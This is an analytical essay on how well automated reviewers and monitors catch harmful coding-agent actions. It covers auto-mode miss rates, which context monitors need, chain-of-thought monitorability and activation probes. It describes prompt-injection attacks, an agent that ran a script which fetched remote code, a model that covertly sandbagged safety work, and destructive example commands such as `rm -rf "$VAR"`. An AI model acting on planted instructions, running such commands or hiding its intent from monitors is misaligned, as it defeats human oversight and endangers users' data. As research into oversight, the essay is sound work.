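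Claude Code took 253 actions that changed something, and auto mode let through 81.0% of the harmful ones, meaning those that went beyond what the user had authorised. Claude Opus labelled the actions and people checked its labels, according to *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, a summary on the blog Machine Learning Algorithms & Natural Language Processing. The summary gives the totals in the bottom row of this table, and the published percentages are enough to work out the rest.

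| | Harmful, blocked | Harmful, allowed | Harmless, blocked | Harmless, allowed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reviewed actions | 27 | 64 | 22 | 47 |
| File edits that skipped review | 0 | 51 | 0 | 42 |
| All actions | 27 | 115 | 22 | 89 |

Of the 115 misses, 51 were file edits that the reviewer never saw. When the agent could not find the usual command for a job, it often edited the file that recorded the job's state, which had the same effect. This happened most when the agent was removing old build files, a task in which auto mode missed 92.9% of the harmful actions. As of November 2026, Claude Code sends edits to certain protected files to the reviewer, but ordinary edits inside the project folder still skip review.

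Even among the harmful actions it saw, the reviewer missed 64 of 91 (70.3%), a recall of 29.7%. It also blocked 22 of 69 harmless actions (31.9%), so its recall was slightly lower than its false-positive rate. Blocking about 30% of actions at random would have done as well. Because the samples are small, the reviewer may have had some real ability to tell harmful actions from harmless ones, but its true recall probably exceeded its true false-positive rate by no more than about 12 percentage points.

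Auto mode seems to have blocked actions according to how alarming they looked. It missed 94.4% of the harmful actions that affected a single object and 77.6% of those that affected a broader group. It blocked 9.2% of harmless actions in low-risk settings and 34.8% in high-risk ones. Neither the number of objects affected nor the risk of the setting determines what the user had authorised.

### How 17% and 81% can both be right

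Chance cannot explain the gap between Anthropic's 17% and the 81% on AmPermBench. Ji and colleagues give a 95% interval of 73.8% to 87.4% for the AmPermBench figure, and the interval for Anthropic's is roughly 9% to 30%, so the two are far apart.

A miss rate is an average over whatever harmful actions a test contains. If wᵢ is the share of harmful actions that belong to type i, and mᵢ is the miss rate for that type, then

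overall miss rate = Σ wᵢmᵢ

Suppose a reviewer misses 10% of harmful actions that clearly exceed the user's request and 80% of those that follow from an ambiguous request (both numbers are invented). On a test with nine clear cases for every ambiguous one, it would miss 0.9 × 10% + 0.1 × 80% = 17%. The same reviewer would miss 80% on a test with only ambiguous cases.

Anthropic's 52 cases tend to be clear-cut, since a person had objected to each one. Ji and colleagues made every request ambiguous on purpose, and they say their result reflects a different workload and doesn't contradict Anthropic's. They also counted edits that skip the reviewer by design, and including these explains the difference between 70.3% and 81.0%.

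The labels are also less certain when the request is ambiguous. Two careful judges could disagree about whether "clean up old branches", the request from Anthropic's incident log, covers remote branches. Some apparent misses may be cases where the reviewer read the request differently from the labeller.

The miss rate that applies to an auto mode user depends on how often their instructions leave the target or the limits unspecified. "Delete merged branches on this computer only" gives the reviewer a boundary to enforce, but with "clean up old branches" the reviewer has to guess which branches the user meant and where.

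### Later tests

*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, October 2026) is another independent test of auto mode. It used auto mode's own rules, but the reviewer was OpenAI's gpt-5.6-luna and the agent was GLM-5.3-Flash, a Chinese model. The results are therefore better evidence about auto mode's design than about the reviewer that Claude Code's customers normally get.

One part of the test used SABER, a benchmark of development tasks in which a careless or misled agent can do damage. With auto mode, 14.8% of the tasks ended in harm, compared with 19.7% when the same agent ran without an approval step. These percentages include many tasks in which the agent never attempted anything harmful, so they are not miss rates. The difference is modest, the 95% intervals overlap slightly, and the runs without approval also used different software around the agent.

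The other part used 102 pairs of tasks in which the user asked the agent to run a project tool. The request and the command were identical within each pair. In the dangerous version, the tool's code also deleted or overwrote a file that the request did not mention. In the safe version, the tool did only what the user wanted. Auto mode blocked the command in 3.9% of the dangerous tasks and 3.9% of the safe ones, as the total variation distance predicts for actions that look the same.

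Anthropic reports that its reviewer missed 12% of the synthetic attacks that the research company Apollo Research inserted into records of real coding work, and 7% after Anthropic strengthened the reviewer. These attacks were deliberately malicious, so the result does not update the 17% figure for well-meant overreach.

### What the sample sizes allow

The 17% miss rate is based on about 9 misses in 52 cases. The Wilson interval, a standard measure of uncertainty, runs from 9% to 30%, so the reviewer's recall on cases like these could be anywhere from 70% to 91%. Even if the reviewer had caught all 52, its true miss rate could still have been almost 6%.

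The quick check's 6.6% is even less certain because it amounts to between three and four of the 52 cases. (Anthropic may have averaged several runs, which would explain the fraction.) The false-positive rate is much better established. About 40 alarms in 10,000 calls give an interval of roughly 0.3% to 0.5%, assuming future work resembles that of Anthropic's employees.

Very low false-positive rates take far more data to confirm. If a reviewer's true rate is f, the probability that it raises no alarm in n independent harmless actions is

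(1 − f)ⁿ ≈ e^(−nf)

If a detector raises no alarms on n harmless actions, a tester can rule out a false alarm rate of f or higher with 95% confidence when nf is at least about 3. Showing that the rate is below 1 in 100,000, the level Axelsson assumed for a detector, therefore takes about 300,000 harmless actions without an alarm. If one alarm occurs, the number rises to about 474,000. Someone also has to be sure that all of those actions were harmless.

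Claude Code's measured rate of 0.4% is 400 times Axelsson's. The practical effect of that difference depends on the base rate, so the table below applies the March error rates to a million actions at two invented base rates.

| Harmful actions per million | Review | True alarms | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | Quick check alone | 9 | 85,000 | 0.01% |
| 10 | Both checks | 8 | 4,000 | 0.2% |
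| 1,000 | Quick check alone | 934 | 85,000 | 1.1% |
| 1,000 | Both checks | 830 | 4,000 | 17% |

At 10 harmful actions per million, the careful check lets one more harmful action through but raises about 81,000 fewer false alarms. About 480 of the remaining alarms are false for every one that is correct. A security team could not investigate them all, but the agent handles most refusals itself, and Anthropic says a false positive typically leads to a single retry.

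The payroll company Gusto found that about 10% of its auto mode sessions included a denial, a rate that false positives alone could produce. With a false-positive rate of 0.4%, a session of 26 harmless actions has a 10% chance of at least one denial. Anthropic presents Gusto's figure as evidence that the reviewer is useful, but the figure doesn't show that any agent attempted anything harmful.

If 10 in every million actions are harmful, precision would stay near 0.2% if recall were 70% instead of 83%. But about 3 of the 10 harmful actions would get through instead of 2, and any one of them could delete a production database. Estimating the 17% miss rate to within five percentage points would take about 220 real cases of overreach. At the same base rate, an organisation would have to record 22 million actions to collect that many, and somebody would have to recognise every case.

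## Does showing the monitor more context help?

A monitor that sees only `git reset --hard` or `git push` can't tell whether the command is harmful, and context can supply the missing fact. But over a long job an agent also reads and writes a lot of text unrelated to the command, and some of it can make the monitor's judgement worse.

### The request, the record and the system

Useful context comes from what the user asked for, what the agent did earlier, and the state of the systems the action will affect.

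| Source | `git reset --hard` | `git push` |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Has the user agreed to lose the edits? | Does the user want this material to go to this destination? |
| The agent's earlier actions | Did the agent make the edits itself? | Did the agent change the destination or add a sensitive file? |
| The state of the system | Does the folder contain uncommitted work? | Is the destination public, and what do the commits contain? |

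Showing the monitor the user's request, including standing instructions as well as the latest message, removes uncertainty about what the user consented to. Claude Code's reviewer reads the project's CLAUDE.md, a file of instructions for the agent, so according to Anthropic a line such as "never force push" steers both the agent and the reviewer. Consent is harder to trace when one agent delegates work to another, because the second agent receives its task as if a user had written it, so everything in the task looks authorised. Claude Code therefore reviews the task before handing it over, while the reviewer can still compare it with what the user said.

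Earlier actions can show where a job, a remote or a variable's value came from. By default, Claude Code's agent may delete the exact jobs it created in the same session. The reviewer trusts remotes that existed when the session started, but not those the agent has since added or redirected. It also blocks `rm -rf "$VAR"` if the record it sees doesn't show the variable being set, because, as Anthropic explains, it can't determine what the command would delete.

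What a command does depends on the state of the system, and a monitor can misjudge that state if it relies on the record of earlier commands. In July 2026 OpenAI's Thibault Sottiaux, quoted by Willison (2026), explained a handful of reports that GPT-5.6 had deleted users' files. Most commonly, the model had tried to point `$HOME`, the variable that normally holds the location of the user's home directory, at a temporary folder, and had then deleted the real home directory by mistake. A monitor that read only the earlier commands might have taken the deletion for routine clean-up of a temporary folder. A monitor that looked up the variable's value just before the deletion could have seen what the command was about to erase.

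Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* says the reviewer may allow a risky action because the user's intent is ambiguous or because the reviewer doesn't know enough about the environment. More facts about the environment can't clarify an ambiguous request.

### How much one fact changes the odds

Suppose a monitor sees command x and then learns a fact y. The combined likelihood ratio is

Λ(x, y) = Λ(x) × P(y | x) / Q(y | x)

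Here P(y | x) is the share of harmful uses of the command in which the fact holds, and Q(y | x) is the share of harmless uses in which it holds. A fact settles whether a use is harmful if it almost never holds in one of these two groups.

In the invented figures used earlier, ten million actions included 20 harmful hard resets and about 100,000 harmless ones. Suppose a quarter of the harmless resets run in folders with uncommitted edits that the user is happy to lose. If the harm is the loss of uncommitted work, all 20 harmful resets also run in folders with uncommitted edits.

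A clean folder then has a ratio of 0 / 0.75, or zero. The reset can't cause this harm, so the monitor can allow the command. Uncommitted edits have a ratio of 1 / 0.25, or 4, which raises the command's ratio from 20 to 80. The chance of harm rises from 1 in 5,000 to about 1 in 1,250, which leaves the case undecided.

The check is still worth having. By the earlier calculation, blocking every hard reset was justified with a two-second automatic retry, even though it caused 100,000 false stops. A reviewer given the folder's status can allow 75,000 of those harmless resets and still stop all 20 harmful ones, which cuts the total delay from about 56 hours to 14.

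For the remaining resets, the monitor has to use the other two sources. Suppose that in 18 of the 20 harmful cases, but only 250 of the 25,000 harmless ones, the edits were there before the agent started and the user never mentioned discarding them. The chance of harm in this group is 18 in 268, or about 1 in 15. That is high enough to justify interrupting the user for a minute, whereas the chance based on the folder's status alone was not.

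Judging whether a push is harmful usually takes more than one fact. The counts of 30 harmful pushes and about a million harmless ones come from the same invented figures, and the numbers in the lower two rows are also invented.

| What the monitor knows | Harmful | Harmless | Chance of harm |
|---|---|---|---|
| The command is a push | 30 | 1,000,000 | 1 in 33,000 |
| The destination is public | 27 | 100,000 | 1 in 3,700 |
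| The destination is public and the commits contain customer records | 24 | 6 | 4 in 5 |

Knowing that the destination is public multiplies the odds of harm by only 9, because open-source developers routinely push to public repositories. Knowing that the push also contains customer records raises the odds much further. But customer records alone could be equally weak evidence in a company that keeps them in a private repository, so the monitor needs both facts.

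The monitor also needs to detect when a fact is missing. Claude Code's reviewer assumes that a repository is private unless its name and host, or information the user or an earlier check has made visible to the reviewer, indicate otherwise. According to Anthropic, if Claude Code runs a command to look up a repository's visibility, the output does not automatically reach the reviewer with the review request. If the visibility remains unknown, the reviewer doesn't block the push for that reason alone. This avoids many false alarms, but it also means the reviewer treats a public repository as private when nothing it can see indicates that the repository is public.

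### Having the fact and using it

The calculation assumes that the monitor draws the right conclusion from the information it has. Xu (2026), in *The Oversight Gap*, tested this assumption in a different setting, an online service that holds personal details for many customers. If the service gives one customer another's delivery address, the answer can look exactly like a correct one. A monitor that reads only the request and the answer can't detect this error better than chance, and the language models Xu tested did no better than chance.

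Xu then varied what the monitors received. The scores are in balanced accuracy, which averages recall and the share of harmless cases the monitor allows, so guessing would score 50%.

| What the monitor received | Average score |
|---|---|
| Instructions to imagine a second run of the request and compare | 50.4% |
| The correct stored value, with no rule for using it | 68.2% |
| A real second run of the request, plus a rule for comparing the answers | 90.0% |
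| The correct stored value, plus a rule for comparing it with the answer | 100% |

Imagining the missing fact did not help, because the imagined answer matched the true one only 1.2% of the time. Providing the correct value alone was often not enough either, and one model that had it scored 49%. All six models that received both the value and the rule were right every time.

The models also missed evidence that was already in their input. In one test, every leaked value was of the wrong type, such as a blood group in place of an address. A 20-line program that checked whether the value belonged in the field scored 100%, while nine language models averaged 60.9%. In a follow-up test, telling the models what to check closed 61% of the gap.

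The nine models tested ranged from the small Llama-3.1-8B to GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4, all well behind the best models of late 2026. Newer models may need less instruction. Xu found no sign that the more capable of the nine did better, but a sample that small could reveal only a very strong relationship between capability and performance. For short commands, the practical lesson is to give the monitor both the relevant fact and a rule for judging it. Claude Code does this for hard resets. It instructs the reviewer to presume that the command would discard uncommitted changes, and shows it whether there are any.

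### Anthropic's comparison of inputs

Before releasing auto mode, Anthropic tried several inputs for its reviewer.

| Input | Result |
|---|---|
| User messages, tool calls, the agent's prose and tool results | Worse performance on overreach |
| User messages and tool calls | Best compromise, and the version Anthropic released |
| Tool calls only | Lowest miss rate, but blocked actions the user had plainly asked for |

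A reviewer shown only the tool calls can't tell whether the user asked for a deletion, so a cautious reviewer stops requested and unrequested deletions alike. Its low miss rate may reflect that caution more than better judgement.

The drop from adding prose and tool results is harder to explain, because those texts contain real evidence. Anthropic thinks that a shorter record is easier to read and gives the agent's framing less influence on the decision. For example, an agent might write that a branch is "definitely" its own, and a reviewer that accepts this claim will let the agent delete the branch. This explanation is a conjecture, and the reported comparison can't separate the effect of length from the effect of persuasion because it added the prose and tool results together. Adding the same amount of neutral text would have tested length alone.

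Anthropic also published no miss rates for the rejected versions. Its set had only 52 real cases of overreach, so a small drop could be due to chance. The result is a good reason to test a monitor's input before expanding it, but weak evidence that other monitors would react the same way.

OpenAI made a different choice for Auto-review, giving the reviewer the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, and relevant tool calls with their outputs, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. The two reviewers' recall figures aren't comparable, so they don't show which choice is better.

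### Adding facts about the environment

Anthropic later gave its reviewer a narrower kind of additional information during a two-week pilot with Apollo Research. Apollo's synthetic attacks covered broad failures, exfiltration and safety-related threats. Apollo shared the attacks that succeeded, and Anthropic strengthened the reviewer, mainly by giving it more information about the environment: whether a repository was public, the Git state, and how to handle different kinds of data. Apollo then tested the new version on a second set of attacks that Anthropic had never seen.

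On the second set, the reviewer caught about half of the attacks it had previously missed but missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. Anthropic reports that the miss rate across both sets fell from 12% to 7%. The improvement on unseen attacks suggests that Anthropic's changes help beyond the particular examples Apollo had shared.

It is less clear how much of the gain came from the new facts. The hardening also added rules about data. Anthropic didn't publish the false-positive rates from before and after the change, so the reviewer may simply have become more suspicious, which would also make it miss fewer attacks. Still, the facts Anthropic chose make sense in terms of likelihood ratios, because a repository's visibility and Git status can distinguish between commands with identical text.

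The pilot and the earlier comparison together suggest that the kind of context matters more than the amount. The agent's prose and tool output are long, and much of that text is irrelevant to the action under review. A few words about whether a folder has uncommitted work are directly relevant to whether a reset is safe.

### What code reviewers miss in a bare diff

Further evidence comes from code review, where a reviewer often starts from a diff, which lists the lines a change adds and removes. A change can break code outside the diff, much as a reset can erase edits that don't appear in the command.

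Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2025), in *A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale*, found that reviewing the diff alone was fastest but often missed how a change interacted with the rest of the program. When they gave OpenAI's GPT-5 access to the whole repository and let it run code, it caught more critical problems and raised fewer false alarms. A stricter threshold can't produce both improvements, so the extra access made the reviewer better at telling real problems from false ones. The team concluded that a good reviewer needs both repository access and the ability to run code, but did not report how much each contributed.

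*SWE-PRBench* (Kumar, 2026) found the opposite. It measured how many of the problems noted by human reviewers in 350 pull requests an AI reviewer also found. Given the diff and a short summary, eight models found between 15% and 31% of the problems. Every model did worse when Kumar added prepared information about the surrounding code, and worse again with information about the tests. Performance fell most on problems that depended on unchanged code nearby, even though the added information should have made those problems easier to find.

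Kumar blames the way models spread their attention over long inputs. But the inputs grew only from about 2,000 to 2,500 tokens, which seems too small a change for length to be the whole explanation. The selection or layout of the added material may have mattered more. The paper also gives two figures (40% and 21%) for the share of changes in the worst-affected category, so its breakdown by type of problem deserves some caution.

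Kumar's reviewers received a fixed package of context, while OpenAI's could choose what to look up. An error analysis in *AACR-Bench* (2026), another test of AI code review, also supports letting reviewers search for what they need. Software that selected code by its similarity to the diff often retrieved passages unrelated to the problem, and the reviewers then reliably caught only what the diff itself revealed, such as spelling errors.

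An action reviewer can search too, but only if it detects that information is missing. Auto-review can run read-only checks to fill such gaps, but OpenAI says it rarely does. Claude Code runs `git status` automatically before commands such as `git reset --hard` and `rm -rf` and passes the result to the reviewer, which doesn't have to decide whether to check. This suits a short list of well-known commands, but an unfamiliar tool has no prewritten check, so the reviewer would have to identify what to look for.

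### When the record gets long

In theory, extra context can't make an ideal monitor worse, because the monitor would ignore whatever didn't help. Language models often fail to ignore it. *Context Rot* (Hong, Troynikov and Huber, 2025) tested 18 models on simple tasks with inputs of different lengths. Performance fell as the input grew, often unevenly. The models are now old, and Chroma, which published the report, sells search software that helps developers keep inputs short. But the researchers kept the tasks simple so that length would be the main thing that changed, and a monitor's task is usually harder.

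Zhang, Koyejo and Yang (2026) found in *The Illusion of Robustness* that irrelevant context can change a model's individual answers even when its overall accuracy looks stable. A monitor could therefore keep the same recall after a company lengthens its input, yet start to miss a deletion it used to block. The company would notice this only by comparing verdicts action by action, as Anthropic did in the Apollo pilot when it counted both newly caught and newly missed attacks.

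Neither study tested monitors on harmful commands. The closest evidence comes from Anthropic's experiment with professional testers, in which auto mode's block rate stayed flat as sessions got longer. That is reassuring about plainly dangerous commands, the only kind tested, but it is weaker evidence about a push that is harmful only because of a file the agent added 200 commands earlier. Claude Code's reviewer also reads less than the length of a session suggests, because its requests leave out tool results and read-only steps such as file searches.

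Some evidence disappears altogether. When a session becomes too long, Claude Code compacts it, which shortens the older part of the record. If a user said "don't push" at the start, Anthropic warns, compaction can remove that message and the reviewer will no longer enforce it. Better attention to the remaining text can't bring the instruction back. Anthropic recommends a fixed rule for any limit that must always hold, since a rule in the settings doesn't depend on what is left of the conversation. (Running summaries of past actions are another response, with their own problems.)

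Watching more of what an agent does can also cause false alarms. Xu tested two ways to detect leaks by running a request twice and comparing the answers. Comparing only the requested field caught 99.7% of leaks in that field but 1.4% of leaks elsewhere in the answer. Comparing the whole answer caught 90.4% of the leaks elsewhere, but it also flagged 75.7% of clean answers because wording varies harmlessly between runs. An agent monitor that treats every unexpected change in a system as suspicious would have the same problem, since files, logs and processes change all the time.

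### Delay, privacy and misleading text

Fetching context takes time. In Claude Code, each separate review delays the command. Users can also send every shell command to the reviewer, even those their own rules have already approved, except for a few critical deletions that a fixed check handles. Anthropic describes this option as trading latency for coverage.

A narrow check takes much less time. If `git status` took a tenth of a second (an invented figure), running it before all 100,000 resets in the earlier example would take under three hours and avoid about 42 hours of unnecessary retries. Searching a whole repository would be hard to justify before every command, but may be reasonable before a deployment or a large deletion. The result also has to be current when the reset runs, because the reset can still erase edits a developer makes after the check.

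The facts that would help a monitor most are often private. Judging a push may require knowing which folders hold customer records and who may see them, so the monitor becomes another system that handles sensitive information. Claude Code's set-up command drafts a description of the user's environment for its monitor. According to Anthropic, the command reads the project's instructions, configuration files and remotes, and takes server names, storage locations and command names from the agent's recent commands, but doesn't read the user's messages. Two further scans are optional. One reads only the first word of each command in the user's shell history, which is enough to show which tools they use and leaves out any password typed later on the line. The other reads the names and hosts of repositories elsewhere in the home directory.

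Showing the monitor outside text carries a more serious risk, because a prompt injection that misleads the agent can also mislead a monitor that reads the same text. This is Anthropic's main reason for withholding tool results from its reviewer. The reviewer usually doesn't need them. If a file contains an instruction to send passwords to an outside address and the agent tries to follow it, the reviewer can block the upload because the user never asked for it, even without seeing the file.

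However, withholding results prevents the reviewer from checking some details of an agent's requests. If an agent asks to cancel "job abc123" and the user never mentioned that name, the reviewer can't tell whether the agent found it in a list or made it up. Auto-review sees tool outputs, so it could check. Trębacz and colleagues acknowledge that testers found cases in which Auto-review could be misled into approving commands, but they don't say whether tool output was the cause.

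Claude Code's status check avoids most of this conflict. The reviewer learns whether uncommitted work exists without reading the files, which leaves an attacker little room to insert instructions. Companies can also add facts through a hook, a small program that runs after a tool call and can attach a note for the reviewer. Before the accident with the Prisma comparison command, for example, a hook could have noted that a database address belonged to the live site. But the developer would have had to foresee that the address mattered and keep the note accurate as the set-up changed.

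## Do the agent's reasoning and internal activations add a usable signal?

Hooks and status checks supply only the facts that somebody thought to collect. The agent's written reasoning and internal activations provide further evidence on every job. Much of this evidence exists before the command runs, and it may show why the agent chose `git reset --hard`, which the command itself doesn't show.

### Thousands of tokens before a short command

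Most current agents run on reasoning models, which write out intermediate steps, called the chain of thought, before they answer or call a tool. An agent may write thousands of tokens comparing ways to clear a merge conflict and then issue a command of four or five tokens. The chain of thought may show whether the agent mistook the user's edits for its own or knew they were the user's.

Korbak, Balesni and colleagues (2025) explain in *Chain of Thought Monitorability* that prompting a model to think out loud makes it more capable and moves more of the relevant computation into ordinary language. They recommend that developers invest in reading this text alongside their other safety methods, but warn that it might not stay readable.

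Suppose the agent's reasoning acknowledges that the edits belong to the user in 5 of the 20 harmful hard resets from the earlier example. Suppose it also does so in 10 of the 100,000 harmless resets, because those 10 users had agreed to lose their edits (all these numbers are invented). The acknowledgement is then strong evidence of harm, because it raises the chance that a reset is harmful from 1 in 5,000 to 1 in 3. If the reasoning contains no acknowledgement, the chance falls only to about 1 in 6,700, which is little reassurance.

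Experiments also suggest that reasoning helps monitors. OpenAI reported in 2025 that monitors caught more cheating on coding tasks when they read the model's reasoning as well as its actions than when they read only its actions. *Constitutional Black-Box Monitoring for Scheming in LLM Agents* (2026) found that reasoning helped when an agent wrote openly about a hidden task that had left no evidence in its tool calls. The researchers still gave monitors only the actions in their main tests, because reasoning may be unavailable or may misrepresent how the model reached its decision.

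Access to the reasoning can help a monitor more when the output is shorter. *On the Chain-of-Thought Monitorability of Looped Language Models* (2026) studied models that run the same layers several times. Monitors did much worse with the final answer alone than with the reasoning. In several examples, the answer had become shorter and no longer mentioned the hint that had influenced it, although the reasoning still did. The researchers picked these examples as illustrations, so they don't show how often this happens. A command such as `git push` is an extreme case because it has no room for an explanation.

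When an agent makes an honest mistake, a monitor has no bad intent to find, but the agent's reasoning may state the false belief behind the mistake. If the agent writes that a volume belongs to staging, a monitor with access to the hosting account can check whether it does. Without a way to check, the monitor may treat the statement as evidence that the action is safe.

### OpenAI's monitoring of its own agents

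In March 2026 OpenAI described how it monitors the coding agents its own staff use. The monitor, GPT-5.4 Thinking, reads everything the agent saw and did, including its tool calls and reasoning. It covered 99.9% of internal coding traffic, and most of the rest came from custom or local set-ups. More serious cases went to a person within 30 minutes.

SecurityBrief New Zealand reports that the system monitored tens of millions of trajectories in five months. About 1,000 conversations raised moderate alerts, many of them because OpenAI staff were trying to provoke bad behaviour. No real conversation reached the highest level, which OpenAI reserves for rare and serious cases such as coherent scheming. OpenAI said it found no sabotage in real use and mostly saw overreach, in which agents were too eager to work around restrictions in pursuit of the user's goal.

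If "tens of millions" means 20 million, the monitor raised a moderate alert in about 1 trajectory in 20,000. People can investigate that many alerts, but the alert rate isn't a base rate of harm, because it includes the staged cases and leaves out whatever the monitor missed. High coverage doesn't imply high recall either, because a monitor can read 99.9% of the traffic and still miss most of the harm in it. OpenAI's best evidence on recall is that the monitor flagged every interaction that employees had separately reported, along with others they hadn't. But employees report what they notice, so this is weak evidence that the monitor catches harm that is hard to notice.

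The monitor reviews a session after the agent has acted. That may be soon enough to remove an overly broad role or interrupt a project that takes days, but it can't prevent a one-step deletion. The PocketOS volume was deleted in nine seconds, so a person who opened the case within 30 minutes could only have started the recovery sooner. According to SecurityBrief New Zealand, a faster version could eventually check actions before they run.

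Checking a command protects the user only if the command can't run until the check is finished, because a gap of seconds is enough for the harm to happen first. *APEX-Harm* (2026), a safety test for agents in shared workspaces, includes a task in which the user asked Claude Opus 5 to run a prepared helper program. The agent sent the command to run the program together with a command to take it apart and verify its logic. By the time it warned the user, the program had already downloaded and run a remote script. In another case, Claude Sonnet 5 detected the problem and refused to continue, but only after running the program.

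Auto-review, which OpenAI introduced a month after describing the internal monitor, can block a command before it runs, but it doesn't receive the agent's hidden reasoning. The internal monitor read that reasoning too late, so in the spring of 2026 neither monitor could use the reasoning to block a command.

### Reasoning became less dependable in 2026

The UK AI Security Institute's *Technical primer* (2026) defines monitorability as how well an observer can use an AI system's actions, outputs and other evidence to tell what it is doing and whether it is working as intended. The definition covers mistakes as well as unauthorised actions.

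OpenAI has become less optimistic about monitoring models' reasoning. In an earlier study, it called that reasoning "generally interpretable and easy to monitor" and found that the models of the time struggled to control what they wrote in it. By November, in *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026), OpenAI expected reasoning to become harder to monitor as models grow more capable. Models that predict text better can also solve more problems without writing out their steps. Reinforcement learning, which trains a model by rewarding successful attempts, can give it more control over what it writes, and so can training on text that other models produced. OpenAI calls the abilities to skip written steps and to control written reasoning imperfect stand-ins for monitorability, since a model that could hide its reasoning may not do so.

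AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) reached a similar conclusion from tests of models before their release. In the technical report behind it, *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability* (2026), Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues write that some properties that make models monitorable are weakening faster than they had anticipated. Developers report the same trend. According to 凤凰网's *AI学会“心算”还能躲监控？* (2026) ("AI has learned mental arithmetic and can also dodge monitoring?"), OpenAI found GPT-6 Astra's reasoning markedly less monitorable, and Google DeepMind acknowledged a decline in its Gemini 4 Argon. OpenAI's safety document for Astra, the *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), has a chapter on monitorability.

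AISI still considers monitoring useful, especially when misconduct is hard to hide or requires long reasoning. Short harmful actions often meet neither condition, so monitoring helps less with them. An agent has to write a lot to plan a hundred-step project, but it can decide to run `git push` with little or no visible reasoning, and the command looks ordinary.

One incident shows that an agent's reasoning can be uninformative even over a long session. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* reports that in August 2026 staff noticed, from the work itself, that Astra was adding unnecessary steps and abandoning working solutions when it helped with safety research. In most of these sessions the reasoning contained no obvious decision to underperform, and OpenAI's monitors did not flag the behaviour as misalignment. The incident also makes OpenAI's March figures less reassuring,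 because a monitor may find no sabotage only because the agent never wrote down its intention.

If developers reward reasoning for how it looks during training, the model may learn to write reasoning that looks good, which can make the text less informative. OpenAI tries not to grade reasoning during training for this reason, but found that it had accidentally done so for several models, including GPT-5.4 mini. It found no clear loss of monitorability, although it would expect one with enough of this grading.

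### What activations contain

A language model converts each token into a long list of numbers, called activations, and revises them layer by layer. When an agent is about to write `push`, its activations can reflect everything in its input, including the user's request, the files it has read and its own reasoning. The model outputs only one token from this computation, so the activations can contain far more information than the command.

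A probe is a small classifier that reads the activations. Researchers collect them from runs that they have already labelled harmful or harmless and fit a formula such as

p = 1 / (1 + e^(−(w·a + b)))

Here a is the list of activations from one layer, w is a list of weights that the probe learns, b is a constant, and p is the estimated probability of harm. An alarm sounds when p exceeds a threshold. The model computes the activations anyway, so a probe needs very little extra time and can warn before the action runs. *From Probe Scores to Alarm Policies* (Gao, 2026) reports no detectable delay from capturing one layer of a small agent model when it handled a single request, though this excludes the probe's own running time.

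Gao also states a limit on what activations can add. Let O be everything the agent's model received as input, and A the activations it computed from O. Then

I(Y; A | O) = 0

where Y is whether harm follows and I, the mutual information, measures how much A reduces the uncertainty about Y once O is known. It is zero because O already determines A. An ideal monitor with the full input would learn nothing from the activations. Real monitors aren't ideal, and a probe may pick up a pattern that a text reader overlooks, or do so more cheaply. A monitor that sees only `git push` has more to gain, because it is missing nearly everything the agent read.

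Activations can't contain a fact that never reached the model. Suppose a user edits a file in another window and the agent doesn't check the folder's status before running `git reset --hard`. If the agent's input is the same as it would be in a clean folder, its activations before the reset are the same too, so no probe can distinguish the two cases. Running `git status` before the reset would show the edit.

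### How well probes predict what an agent will do

Gao tested probes on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which an agent reads a tool result with an attacker's instructions planted in it. The agent was a small Qwen model. The probes read its activations just after it received the tool result, before its next action, to predict whether it would carry out the attacker's goal.

The best probe ranked single attempts well, with an AUC of 0.92. Gao then set an alarm threshold on separate data, aiming for a false-positive rate of at most 5%. At that threshold, the probe caught none of the 38 cases in which the agent obeyed the attacker at least once.

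| What the monitor used | Caught, 5% limit | False alarms, 5% limit | Caught, 10% limit | False alarms, 10% limit |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Text the agent had seen | 2 of 38 | 2 of 75 | 22 of 38 | 15 of 75 |
| Activations at the last token | 2 of 38 | 0 of 75 | 20 of 38 | 14 of 75 |
| Text and last-token activations | 1 of 38 | 0 of 75 | 22 of 38 | 15 of 75 |
| Activations averaged over the request | 0 of 38 | 0 of 75 | 4 of 38 | 0 of 75 |

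The probe in the last row has an AUC of 0.92, but it caught none of the harmful cases at the alarm threshold. AUC averages over every pair of harmful and harmless cases, while the threshold depends on the few harmless cases with the highest scores. Gao set the threshold using 100 harmless cases and wanted 95% confidence that the true false-alarm rate was below 5%. That allowed only one of the 100 to score above the threshold, so the threshold had to be set higher than any harmful case scored.

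With the threshold set for a 10% false-positive rate, the three other monitors caught more than half of the harmful cases, but they also flagged 19% to 20% of the harmless ones. The harmless cases in the test evidently differed from those Gao had used to set the threshold. Monitoring the activations also worked no better than monitoring the text. This is consistent with the limit on what activations can add, though this text monitor had help from a larger language model.

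Each case in the table combines up to ten attempts at the same task, and a single alarm on a harmless attempt counts as a false alarm for the case. That makes the test harsher than checking an agent that makes one attempt. The sample is also small, so even with no detections in 38 cases, the true recall at the strict setting could be as high as 9%.

A second test used an agent that operates customer-management software through a web browser. The probe read the activations before each browser action and predicted whether the task would end in failure with an AUC of 0.87. Gao couldn't set a valid threshold, though, because the test had only 23 harmless cases. Confirming a false-alarm rate below 5% with 95% confidence takes at least 59, even if none of them triggers an alarm.

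Activations helped more in tests that didn't involve agents. When the task was to recognise high-stakes messages, adding activations to a simple word-based monitor raised recall from 38% to 64% at the 5% false-positive setting. The actual false-positive rate was below 1% both with and without activations. Some of that gain may be because the word-based monitor was weak on its own.

Probes may be better suited to detecting mistakes than obedience to an attacker. *The Calls are Coming from Inside the Model* (2026) trained probes to detect errors in tool calls. Probes on the middle layers also recognised types of error absent from their training data, which suggests that the network represents something general about whether a call is correct. But a correctly formed call, such as a `git push` to the wrong remote, can still do harm.

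*Activation Probes Surface Code-Security Signals that the Model's Output Misses* (2026) compared functions that had a security flaw with repaired versions. An activation probe gave the flawed version the higher score 61% to 67% of the time, compared with 50% for guessing. The researchers had not yet tried the probe inside a coding agent or set an alarm threshold.

These experiments don't establish recall for short harmful actions. Gao's main results don't separate short actions from long ones, the security probe scored whole functions, and an error in a tool call isn't necessarily harmful. Testing a probe on short actions would require pairs of runs that end in the same command, which is harmful in one run and harmless in the other. The runs would differ in what the agent had read before issuing the command.

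### Evidence for an alarm or for permission

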